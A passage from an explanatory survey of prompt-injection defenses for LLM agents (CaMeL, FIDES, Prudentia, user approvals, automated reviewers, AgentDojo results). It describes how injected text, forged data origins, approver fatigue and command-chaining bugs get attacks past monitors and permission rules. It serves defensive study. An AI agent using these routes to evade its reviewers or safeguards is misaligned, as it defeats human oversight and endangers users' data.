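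### Errors as ordinary values

Tallam and Miller propose closing the error channel by having tools return a result marked as a success or an error, which the program handles like any other value. In the appointment example, a missing appointment would no longer stop the program, so Bob would get his reply either way.

This works only if outsiders can see the same thing whether the step succeeds or fails. If the program checks the result and emails Bob only after a success, the leak returns as an ordinary branch, which the interpreter has to track. The planner must also allow for failure at every step, which makes its programs longer. Garby and colleagues give their agent functions that return errors this way, but report that many errors in LLMbda can't be handled so. They consider the lack of error recovery a considerable weakness of the agent.

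### Padding the run time

A system can hide timing differences by padding every sensitive step to the longest time any of them could take. Tallam and Miller borrow this technique from cryptographic software, where operations are short and predictable. Model calls vary much more, so padding them can add long delays. If a call usually takes two seconds but can take thirty, ten padded calls take five minutes instead of twenty seconds. If the provider has no firm upper limit on response time, the system also needs a deadline, and a missed deadline is another visible failure.

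Random delays add less overhead but only slow the attack. If the delays are independent, an outsider can reduce the random variation tenfold by averaging a hundred measurements.

Fu and colleagues found that padding the model's internal work suppressed the signal they were using, but required extra computation. Moving the approval rule from the prompt into separate trusted software also suppressed the signal, because the model no longer processed the rule. This supports enforcing policies outside the model, but someone still has to give that software reliable information about each action and who authorised it.

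### Rehearsal on artificial data

Garby and colleagues replace CaMeL's retry loop with a rehearsal, called *randori*, in which the agent corrects its mistakes before it sees any real data. They needed an alternative because LLMbda also tracks the retry loop. If an attempt reads untrusted data and fails, the conversation becomes untrusted, and so does every plan the model later writes in it.

1. The planner writes a program for the user's task.
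2. The interpreter runs it on an artificial bank account. The tool for reading files always returns the same placeholder text, and the tools for payments and password changes do nothing.
3. If the program fails, the planner receives the error and writes a new program. This continues until a program succeeds or the planner runs out of attempts.
4. The planner writes a final version, with instructions not to rely on names or descriptions from the artificial data.
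5. The interpreter runs the final version on the real account.

The errors in step 3 can't reveal the real balance or contain an attacker's text, because the rehearsal uses neither. The rehearsal also avoids a danger of retrying on a live account, where a program might pay a bill, fail at a later step, and pay it again on the next attempt.

But the rehearsal is a limited test. Placeholder text can't show whether a program will find the account number in a real invoice. The final version is also new code that hasn't run even on the artificial account, and the agent proceeds to it even if every rehearsal failed. The rehearsal currently lacks label checks, and Garby and colleagues suggest adding simulated ones. The planner could then correct a plan that fails these checks and still learn nothing about the real account.

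## User approvals

When a tool call in a live run fails a policy check, the system can refuse the call or ask the user to approve it. Asking lets many legitimate tasks finish, including the email to Bob, whose address comes from notes that other people can edit. It also makes the user part of the defense, because the system will stop a forged address only if the user notices it.

Microsoft ships FIDES as an experimental part of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. By default, FIDES blocks tool calls that violate its policy, but developers can have it ask the user for approval instead. The documentation recommends blocking for production systems in low-trust environments and asking for approval in interactive use, development and testing.

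### How a blocked call becomes a question

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes policies with three possible results: allow, deny and ask. One example governs messages to a Teams channel.

1. The agent proposes a message, and the software attaches labels to the call and to the message text.
2. If the agent had read nothing untrusted when it proposed the call, the policy allows it.
3. Otherwise, the policy looks up the channel's members and compares them with the people who may read the text. If every member may read it, the policy allows the call.
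4. If some members may not, the software pauses and tells the user who would gain access.

An attacker can't persuade the system to skip user approval, because ordinary code uses the labels to determine when approval is required. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) makes this point about Prudentia, a version of FIDES whose planner takes the policies into account and tries to avoid violating them. But the policy still has to require approval at the right moment. Like the looser FIDES rules, the Teams policy doesn't require approval for calls that the planner made without reading untrusted text, so a forged address for Bob could pass without the user's approval.

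The question itself may contain little information. In Agent Framework, it names the tool and the label that caused the block, and Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) concedes that "approvals are coarse". The Teams example identifies the new readers by account ID, which few users would recognise. A fuller dialog for Bob's email might show these items:

| Item | Where it comes from | Can someone who edits the notes change it? |
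|---|---|---|
| The tool, `send_email` | The planner's program | No |
| The reason for asking | The labels and the policy | No |
| The recipient's address | The meeting notes | Yes |
| The attachment's name | The meeting notes | Yes |
| The attachment's contents | The company drive | Yes, by naming a different file |

The first two items explain why the system is asking, but the user has to judge the other three. That may be hard, since the user asked the agent to look up Bob's address and may not know it. To check it, the user needs a second source, such as an address book or an earlier email from Bob. Kolluri and colleagues suggest that the dialog show the labels and the origin of each piece of data. They leave the dialog's design to future work and warn that attackers may try to manipulate what the approver reads.

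### What a "yes" changes

The narrowest kind of approval lets one call run and leaves every label unchanged. Prudentia also lets the user endorse the data itself, so the planner can read it without lowering the trust in its later calls. An LLMbda program can endorse data in a similar way, but in Prudentia a person decides during the task.

Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email containing ten to-do items, each needing a tool call with real consequences. The user has to approve all ten calls separately if the planner reads the email without endorsement, but one approval covers them all if the user endorses the email.

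The single approval is also riskier. Suppose an attacker has added an eleventh item to the email. If the user approved each call, they would see the unexpected action just before it runs. With a single approval, they have to spot the extra item in the text before the agent has proposed anything. If they miss it and endorse the email, the policy for consequential actions will allow the eleventh call. Prudentia does not offer a single approval for sharing secrets. Kolluri and colleagues argue that whether to share private information depends too much on the situation for one blanket permission, so the user must approve each disclosure separately.

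An "always allow" button also approves calls the agent hasn't yet proposed, possibly in later tasks. In *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, Wang, Li and Tian (2026) reviewed 21 agent products and found that such permissions accumulate over time, with no systematic way to reduce them.

### How people answer repeated requests

Wang and colleagues found that 15 of the 21 products asked for approval while the agent was running. Most published data on how users respond come from coding agents, which ask before running certain commands. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users of its coding agent, Claude Code, approved 93 percent of requests, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports 97 percent.

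The share of harmful requests that people reject is a better measure of how carefully they review than the overall approval rate, because most requests are harmless and should be approved. To find that share, Anthropic had a research vendor hire 1,053 professional testers for a coding study. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, rejected it. They rejected about 17 percent of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session, but about 5 percent of those that appeared after 50 or more requests.

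The setting may have made the testers less careful than usual. They knew they were being evaluated, though not on what, and a mistake in the test environment couldn't damage their own projects. Part of the decline could also be because people who approve quickly are more likely to reach fifty requests. Anthropic also had an interest in the result, because it was about to replace these requests with an automated reviewer. Still, these biases would have to be very large for a measured 13.6 percent to be consistent with dependable protection.

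Knowing about the danger doesn't seem to help much. In a survey of developers, *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), 68 percent were very or extremely concerned about leaking secrets, but developers who knew of more incidents didn't approve actions more carefully. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the code an agent wrote, 61 percent often approved at least one type of action without a close look. Developers in safety-critical fields reported more approvals without a close look for six of the seven types of action. These results are self-reported, but they suggest that skilled reviewers inspect code carefully while treating permission requests as interruptions.

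Claude Code users rejected 39 percent of the plans the agent presented for approval, though many of those rejections may have been about the plan's quality rather than its safety. CaMeL could also show the user its finished plan before running it. For Bob's document, the user would see that the address will come from the meeting notes, but not the address itself.

Even careful approvers make mistakes. Willison mentions Troy Hunt, a security researcher who fell for a phishing attack while tired from jet lag. Suppose a user wrongly approves only 1 percent of harmful requests, far fewer than the testers did, and an attacker causes fifty such requests. If the user's errors are independent, the chance of at least one wrong approval is

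1 − 0.99⁵⁰ ≈ 0.395

or about 40 percent. Real errors are probably not independent, because a tired user is likely to make several in a row. The calculation does show how a small error rate adds up when an attacker can keep trying.

An organisation can measure its own approvers the way Anthropic's study did. *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* (2026) recommends planting incorrect but harmless proposals among the real ones, blocking them before they take effect, and recording how long people take to answer and how often they edit or reject a proposal. If people approve everything as a formality, the agent is in practice more autonomous than its settings indicate.

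### How many approvals a task needs

Many ordinary agents ask the user for approval before every consequential call because they can't tell which calls untrusted data has influenced. An agent with labels can limit its requests to calls that break a policy. Kolluri and colleagues counted how many requests this avoids on AgentDojo, using the policies that Costa and colleagues used for FIDES. They ran each agent five times without attacks and assumed that a user would approve every request in a run that completed its task.

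They compared a basic agent that asks before every consequential call, the same agent with labels and policies, FIDES, and Prudentia. These are the average results with OpenAI's o3-mini model:

| Agent | Approvals across all completed tasks | Tasks completed with no approval |
|---|---|---|
| Basic agent | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Basic agent with labels and policies | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
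| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

Prudentia's approval figure is calculated from the 2.9-fold reduction that Kolluri and colleagues report. Across AgentDojo's 97 user tasks, the basic agent needed roughly one approval for every two tasks, and FIDES roughly one for every five. With a different model, o4-mini, FIDES needed 36.8 approvals and Prudentia 19.2, but Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2 percent, compared with 75.7 percent for FIDES).

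With o3-mini, labels and policies alone account for about half of the reduction in approvals, because the agent no longer asks about calls that satisfy a policy. Most of the rest comes from hiding untrusted text from the planner, as FIDES does. Prudentia's planner must justify opening a hidden variable and list the calls it expects to make afterwards, and it can ask for an endorsement if one would replace several approvals. On WASP, a benchmark of attacks on agents that use a web browser, Prudentia needed no approvals, while the basic agent needed between 1.00 and 3.65 per task on average. But WASP's user tasks are posting a comment or upvoting a post, which the agent can do without reading untrusted content. The agent will still ask for approval when a task requires it to act on an email's contents.

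Real users would also see more requests than these totals suggest, because Kolluri and colleagues counted only runs that completed the task. In most of the failed runs, the agent kept trying calls that broke a policy, and a user would have had to reject them or stop the agent. The study doesn't measure whether people answer more carefully when they receive fewer requests. Its result of zero successful attacks on AgentDojo assumes that a person would catch every harmful call the software passed on for approval.

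### Risk tiers, standing rules and sandboxes

Another way to reduce approval requests is to save them for the actions that could do the most harm. Tallam and Miller propose three tiers for CaMeL. In the green tier, the agent can read public or openly shared data after a basic check of its source. In the yellow tier, changes within the user's own environment need a quick confirmation if any argument is untrusted. In the red tier, actions that are irreversible or visible to outsiders, such as sending email, keep the full policy checks and need approval through more than one factor, such as a password and a code from a phone.

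Tallam and Miller didn't test the tiers on CaMeL. They write that similar schemes preserved over 90 percent of legitimate work and blocked every simulated attack, but the source they cite is a general guide to defining such access rules. They also put moving a file to a shared folder in the yellow tier, which is doubtful because the move could expose the file to everyone with access to the folder. In the red tier, a second factor confirms who is approving the email to Bob, but not whether the address is Bob's.

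Standing rules settle common cases before the agent starts. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes how the company restricts network access when it uses Codex, its coding agent. The agent can contact expected sites, can't contact certain others, and needs approval for unfamiliar ones. A similar rule for email could let the agent send messages to addresses in the company directory, such as Bob's real address, and require approval for any others.

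Too many approval requests can leave a system less protected than fewer would, because people who tire of them tend to write rules that are too broad. By June 2026, 49.5 percent of active Claude Code command-line users had created a rule that allows certain shell commands. Many of these rules allow any command that starts with `python`, which in practice permits almost any action. OpenAI found the same kind of rule among a sizable minority of its own staff. Anthropic also reports that a quarter of interactive sessions start with permission checks turned off.

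A sandbox, an isolated environment that restricts which files and networks an agent can reach, reduces approval requests without relying on anyone's judgment. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) illustrates this with 10,000 actions by Codex inside OpenAI. Codex carried out 9,280 of them within the sandbox, and only the other 720 needed approval. The ratio depends on the work. A sandbox helps less with an email assistant, because every email it sends has to leave the sandbox.

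### Automated reviewers

OpenAI and Anthropic now offer a language model that answers the remaining requests in the user's place. OpenAI says its version, Auto-review, changes only who approves requests and leaves the sandbox's limits as they were. Of the 720 requests above, the model approved 713 and denied seven. After four of the denials, the agent found a safer way to continue. After the other three, it stopped to ask the user, who would otherwise have had to answer all 720 requests.

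Anthropic made its version, auto mode, the default for new Claude Code sessions on most of its individual and team plans in August 2026. This weakens an argument that Wang and colleagues had made a few months earlier. They had taken the industry's reliance on human approval as evidence that people judge an agent's actions more reliably than models do. In Anthropic's controlled study, the model did much better than the testers on the same commands, and it also missed far fewer harmful actions in the companies' other tests:

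| Reviewer | Harmful actions tested | Missed |
|---|---|---|
| Paid testers | One dangerous command in each of 1,053 sessions | 86.4% |
| Anthropic's reviewer | The same commands | 11% |
| Anthropic's reviewer, earlier version | 52 real actions that went beyond what users wanted | 17% |
| Anthropic's reviewer, earlier version | 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data | 5.7% |
| OpenAI's reviewer | Synthetic actions that went beyond what users wanted | 9.7% |
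| OpenAI's reviewer | Three kinds of synthetic prompt injection | 0.7% |

These rates come from the companies that sell the products, and the 17 percent is based on so few cases that the true rate could plausibly be between 9 and 30 percent. The 0.7 percent rate rises to 9.8 percent when OpenAI includes attacks that delete or alter data, though Trębacz and colleagues consider most of the additional misses not serious. Even at 0.7 percent, an attacker who made fifty independent attempts would have about a 30 percent chance of succeeding at least once. Automated approval is therefore the kind of statistical defense that labels and policies were supposed to replace. Trębacz and colleagues say that testers misled their reviewer into approving some commands, and that they don't expect such systems to provide deterministic guarantees.

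An outside test of prompt injection provides little evidence of how much protection Anthropic's reviewer adds. None of 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models with auto mode on, but even with permission checks turned off, Anthropic's latest models failed only 0.09 percent of the time on average. The attacks had also been optimised against an older model, and adaptive attacks on the reviewer could succeed more often.

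Wang and colleagues object that an attacker who can manipulate the agent's model may be able to manipulate the reviewer in the same way. Anthropic limits this risk by showing its reviewer only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, not the tool results or the agent's explanations. A sentence hidden in the meeting notes therefore can't instruct the reviewer directly, but the reviewer also can't tell where a value came from. If the agent proposes to email the document to a forged address, the reviewer sees that the user asked for an email to Bob and that the agent is sending one. CaMeL and FIDES record where values came from, and a reviewer could receive their labels without reading the untrusted text. The labels would show that the address came from the notes, but not whether it was Bob's.

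Shell commands pose a similar problem, because the same text can have different effects. In *Shall We Approve?* (2026), a user asks an agent to delete old build files and recompile a program. The agent proposes `make clean && make`, which is harmless in one workspace and dangerous in another. Reviewers that relied on the text blocked dangerous commands but also their harmless counterparts. Predicting a command's effects reduced harm but not unnecessary blocks, while observing the effects reduced both. Caper, a system that observes effects, blocked only 1.0 percent of the harmless counterparts. Observing effects works better for file changes, which a system can inspect and discard, than for emails, which nobody can recall after delivery.

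Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves. It also lists actions that its reviewer should never approve, such as sending secrets outside the organisation, but the reviewer can refuse only those it detects. A FIDES policy that blocks actions instead of asking for approval avoids this weakness if the labels are correct, though it also blocks some legitimate emails.

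## What the test results show

Researchers have tested the main systems on AgentDojo, often both with and without policies enabled. They report the number of successful attacks and utility, the share of user tasks an agent completes.

### FIDES with and without policies

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o against an attacker who knows the agent's tools and plants instructions to call them in a certain order. They compared it with a basic agent and with a variable-passing agent, which hides every tool result from the planner and has no quarantined model to read them. The table gives averages over five runs. The attack column leaves out cases Costa and colleagues judged harmless or wrongly scored. The other columns show utility without attacks, in percent.

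| Agent | Successful attacks | Office workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 152 | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Basic, with policies | 0 | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| Variable-passing | 0 | 47.5 | 43.0 | 57.4 | 38.1 |
| Variable-passing, with policies | 0 | 48.0 | 44.0 | 56.3 | 35.2 |
| FIDES | 21 | 63.5 | 50.0 | 65.0 | 63.8 |
| FIDES, with policies | 0 | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

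Without policies, FIDES let 21 attacks through, about the same as the 20 let through by Tool Filter, a defense without guarantees. Tool Filter asks a language model at the start of a task which tools the task needs, and removes the others. The policies stopped the remaining attacks on FIDES, but they also stopped every attack on the basic agent, whose planner reads all the untrusted text. Under those policies, the advantage of FIDES was that it completed more tasks, an average of 50 percent across the four environments compared with 42 percent for the basic agent.

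The basic agent outperformed FIDES only in travel, where the policies allow many tools to run after the agent has read untrusted text, as long as nothing confidential leaks. The policies therefore rarely blocked the basic agent, while FIDES still had to work with hidden variables, which GPT-4o often handled badly. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68 percent of the travel tasks under the same policies, and its average lead over the basic agent with policies grew to 16 points across all environments.

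FIDES with policies has much lower utility than the basic agent without them. Utility fell from 98.8 to 52.5 percent in banking and from 93.3 to 47.6 percent in Slack. Part of this loss comes from the planner's mistakes and should shrink with better models. With o1 and no policies, FIDES was only 6.3 points behind the basic agent. The rest comes from tasks that the policies forbid, such as following the instructions in a file, which even a better model can't complete without breaking a policy.

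Attacks reduced utility only slightly further, because the planner can continue after a policy blocks a call. FIDES with policies completed 56.9 percent of the banking tasks and 41.9 percent of the Slack tasks under attack.

The utility scores are probably somewhat too high for all the agents. The variable-passing agent was credited with completing some tasks that require reading untrusted text, even though it can't read such text. Costa and colleagues found that in these cases the agent had guessed, AgentDojo's checks were incomplete, or the correct outcome was to do nothing.

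### Separating architecture from enforcement

A system can resist an attack because its planner never put the harmful action in the plan, or because a policy blocked the action. A single score combines both cases, so Garby and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's banking pairs into two groups and report results for each.

In 97 of the 144 pairs, the plan should never contain the action the attacker needs, so the attack should fail without any policy. The other 47 pairs can test enforcement because the plan already contains an action the attacker could use, such as a payment to an account named in a file.

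Garby and colleagues ran each pair three times per model on their LLMbda agent and also reran CaMeL. The last two columns count the attacks each system resisted, so 138/141 means three attacks succeeded. CaMeL's totals are sometimes lower because some runs didn't finish.

| System | Model | Tasks completed without attack | Attacks resisted, 97 architecture pairs | Attacks resisted, 47 enforcement pairs |
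|---|---|---|---|---|
| LLMbda agent | GPT-5.2 | 36/48 | 291/291 | 139/141 |
| LLMbda agent | Qwen3.7-plus | 36/48 | 291/291 | 141/141 |
| LLMbda agent | MiMo-v2.5 | 31/48 | 291/291 | 141/141 |
| CaMeL, no policies | GPT-5.2 | 32/48 | 98/99 | 141/141 |
| CaMeL, no policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 34/48 | 240/241 | 138/141 |
| CaMeL, with policies | GPT-5.2 | 18/48 | 97/97 | 134/134 |
| CaMeL, with policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 18/48 | 216/216 | 141/141 |

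Across the three models, two of 1,296 attacks on the LLMbda agent succeeded. In both, the agent paid a replaced bill. Two-thirds of the runs used architecture pairs, so the more informative figure is two successes in the 423 runs that could test enforcement.

Even that figure is weaker evidence about enforcement than it seems. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL resisted all 141 attacks in the enforcement pairs even with its policies switched off. The plans left room for the attacks to succeed, but the attacks failed, perhaps because the quarantined model ignored the injected text. With MiMo-v2.5, three attacks succeeded without policies and none with them. If policies made no difference and the runs were independent, there would still be about a one-in-eight chance that all three successes occurred in the runs without policies.

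CaMeL's policies reduced its utility on the banking tasks from 66.7 to 37.5 percent with GPT-5.2 and from 70.8 to 37.5 percent with MiMo-v2.5. There are only 16 of these tasks, so the 95 percent confidence intervals extend more than 20 points either way, but the drop was large with both models.

The LLMbda agent has higher utility than CaMeL, at 64.6 to 75 percent with its label checks always on, but some of this advantage comes from more permissive rules. The agent enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and its planner may endorse untrusted values.

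CaMeL's own evaluation reported a much smaller loss. CaMeL completed 77 percent of AgentDojo's tasks under attack with OpenAI's o3, according to *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026), which cites the 2025 preprint of the CaMeL paper. An undefended agent completed 84 percent. CaMeL also used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. The 77 and 37.5 percent figures don't contradict each other, because the two evaluations used different models and covered different tasks. The 77 percent is for all of AgentDojo, while the 37.5 percent is for banking alone, where many tasks require the agent to act on what it reads.

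### What a perfect score supports

A perfect score on a small test is compatible with a fair number of failures in use. When a system resists all of n independent attacks, the lower end of the 95 percent Wilson interval, a standard way to estimate a proportion, is

n / (n + 1.96²)

For 47 pairs, this gives 47 / 50.84, or 92.4 percent. A system that really resists 92.4 percent of such attacks would have about a 2.4 percent chance of passing all 47, since 0.924⁴⁷ ≈ 0.024. A system with a much lower rate would be very unlikely to pass them all.

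Garby and colleagues use the 47 pairs in the formula instead of all 141 runs, because three runs of the same task with the same attack text aren't three independent tests. Using all 141 runs would raise the lower end to 97.3 percent. Even the 47 pairs aren't fully independent, because they come from 16 tasks and nine attacks, so a flaw that affects one pair may affect several others.

If 7.6 percent of attacks succeeded, an attacker who made ten independent attempts would succeed at least once about 55 percent of the time.

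A system would have to pass about 3,800 independent pairs to support a resistance rate of 99.9 percent. That result would still apply only to attacks drawn from the same source as those in the test.

A successful attack can expose a case where a theorem's premises don't hold, such as a mislabelled field or a tool without a check. Tests are more useful for finding these mistakes than for ruling them out, since some could remain after 47 attacks fail.

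### Tests that make the model obey

As models get better at ignoring injected text, ordinary benchmarks become less useful for testing the software around the models. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) tests TypeGuard, its Haskell system, which the latest version of the paper calls ELBA. The test paired AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with five attacks, making 105 pairs, and used four recent models. Every model resisted every attack in both TypeGuard and CaMeL, with policies on or off, so the results provide no evidence that the policies work.

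Zhou and colleagues then changed the software so that the attacks would reach a model that obeyed them. In TypeGuard, the main agent reads outside data by calling a subagent, which normally receives a task followed by the data. When the data contained the marker that opens AgentDojo's injections, the modified software removed the task and gave the subagent only the data, so the attacker's text became the subagent's instructions. The table shows the number of successful attacks and completed user tasks out of 735 runs for each model and setting.

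| Model | Successful attacks, no policies | With policies | Tasks completed, no policies | With policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 310 | 0 | 523 | 351 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 275 | 0 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT-5.4 | 114 | 0 | 558 | 338 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 195 | 0 | 494 | 294 |

This is much better evidence for enforcement than the original 105 pairs, because up to 42 percent of the attacks succeeded without the policies. AgentDojo flagged 29 of the runs with policies as successful attacks, but Zhou and colleagues read all 29 and found no violations. The test still used the same five attack goals. It established that the policies stop those goals when a subagent cooperates, but it didn't include a search for harmful actions that the policies allow.

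The policies also reduced the number of completed tasks by 33 to 44 percent. Garby and colleagues cite a similar loss without attacks, from 15 to 8 of the 21 Slack tasks. They also cite a score of 7 for CaMeL with policies. The latest version of Zhou and colleagues' paper reports a larger advantage over CaMeL, with roughly twice as many tasks completed under policies.

Garby and colleagues report one successful attack on TACIT, the Scala system, in 1,926 trials across all four AgentDojo environments and two models. They argue that every pair tests enforcement because TACIT has no separate planner. But the Slack results show that a recent model may ignore the injected text, so the count alone doesn't show how often TACIT's type checker had to stop anything.

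*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) also reports that agents can write code that passes TACIT's type checker with no significant loss in task performance. TACIT's design assumes that the main model may cooperate fully with the attacker. A test with a model that always obeys injections would match that assumption more closely than AgentDojo does.

Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar (2026), in *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component*, measured what a model attempts separately from what the software allows. They built an environment with 13 tasks and 12 tools, in which a monitor permits only the calls that the user's task requires and also checks where confidential data is going. They chose two small open models that are easy to mislead. Qwen2.5-1.5B proposed the attacker's call in 64 percent of 156 attacks, and Qwen2.5-7B did so in 84 percent.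 The monitor let the attack through in 1.3 and 7.7 percent of cases, respectively. Because the models proposed the attacker's call so often, these low success rates are clearly due mostly to the monitor. The monitor is much simpler than CaMeL or FIDES, so the rates don't apply to either system.

### Fixed and adaptive attacks

Most of AgentDojo's attacks are texts meant to persuade a model. They don't target labels that the interpreter drops or arguments that a policy fails to check. Garby and colleagues found the two label-tracking flaws in CaMeL by studying its interpreter, and the benchmark's attacks exposed neither.

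The boundary laundering that Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated is also easy to miss in a benchmark score. With CaMeL in each agent, the benchmark's attacks succeeded 0.2 percent of the time on average, even though the handover between agents was open to attack.

Aljumaily and colleagues measured how much a fixed test can underestimate the success of attacks. They compared two monitors that check a tool call's arguments, one written naively and one hardened against known tricks, such as adding an extra address to a list of recipients, disguising a file path, or joining several shell commands. When a simulated model made one attempt per task without such tricks, about 15 percent of attacks succeeded against either monitor. When the attacker could make up to 25 attempts and vary the arguments, the success rate rose to 84.6 percent against the naive monitor and 30.8 percent against the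 hardened one.

This comparison used working code for the attacker and the monitors, but it assumed how readily the model would obey injected instructions. A separate count, which doesn't depend on that assumption, covered 33 attack variants that could do harm. A list of allowed tools admitted 27 of them, the naive monitor admitted 18, the hardened monitor admitted 6, and the monitor that limits calls to the user's task admitted 1. Even with that last monitor, a fully compromised model could cause some unauthorised effect in 23.1 percent of simulated runs, for example by writing a false report to a permitted file or putting a phishing link in a permitted email. Stricter checks on arguments don't remove this kind of harm, because the text itself causes it.

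Narisetty and colleagues argue that no one has yet put defenses outside the model through a systematic adaptive test like the one that broke twelve model-based defenses. They ran a small test of this kind on Progent, which lets a language model revise its policy after reading tool results. Their attack tries to get this language model to permit a harmful action by describing it as a routine step that is already authorised.

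The study used Qwen2.5-7B both as the agent and to write the policies, with eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo environments, and was repeated three times. On average, a standard attack succeeded 25.8 percent of the time without a defense and 4.2 percent with Progent. The adaptive attack succeeded 2.6 percent of the time against Progent. It succeeded slightly more often than the standard attack in banking, at 3.7 percent compared with 1.9 percent, but less often in Slack, at 4.2 percent compared with 10.8 percent.

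An adaptive attack that performs worse than a standard one probably wasn't very strong. Narisetty and colleagues suggest that wording meant to reassure the policy model also made the agent less likely to follow the injected instruction. They wrote one template by hand, whereas Nasr and colleagues repeatedly revised their texts based on how the defended system responded. Narisetty and colleagues' paper hasn't been peer reviewed, and their company, LaunchSafe, builds this type of defense. Still, the result agrees with the Progent paper's own tests, in which adaptive attacks succeeded between 0.5 and 4.2 percent of the time.

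Under the standard attack, Progent lowered the share of tasks the agent completed from 45.2 percent to 27.1 percent and raised the number of language model calls per task to about 15 times as many.

Stronger search methods already exist. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026) uses a group of AI agents that share notes as they look for injections that work, and reports that current models still obey some of them. The models included four versions of Gemini, tested with the protections outside the model switched off. The results give another reason not to rely on the model's own resistance, but they don't measure how well an outside defense would resist these attacks.

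A thorough test of CaMeL or FIDES would give the attacker the policies and several ways to get around them. Narisetty and colleagues propose attacks that forge the origin of data, manipulate the person who approves an action, or look for side channels. They would also record how often the system asks for approval, because a system could otherwise score well by passing every difficult decision to the user. They list attacks that use only permitted actions as an open problem. Branch steering, described earlier, is one such attack.

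### Defenses in shipped products

The results above come from research software, but some of these mechanisms are already in products. Microsoft's Agent Framework, for example, includes an experimental version of FIDES. Narisetty and colleagues note that this version treats data as trusted if a developer forgets to label it. Costa and colleagues couldn't have found this risk in their tests, because they applied the untrusted label to every field that the benchmark attacks.

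Other products limit what an agent can reach. Zhou and colleagues cite Chrome's Agent Origin Sets, which restrict which websites a browser agent may read or change. This can keep an injected instruction from sending the agent to an attacker's site. But if the agent may read a site where outsiders can post, the restriction alone doesn't check whether an address posted there is genuine.

Claude Code combines an operating-system sandbox with rules that match shell commands against text patterns. Zhou and colleagues report that a bug in March 2026 weakened those rules. When a command joined several parts with `&&`, Claude Code checked only the first part against its list of forbidden commands. Even without such a bug, a rule that forbids a command for reading a certain file can miss a short Python program that reads the same file. The sandbox can still block the program if the file is outside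 the permitted directories, because it controls file access regardless of how the command is written.
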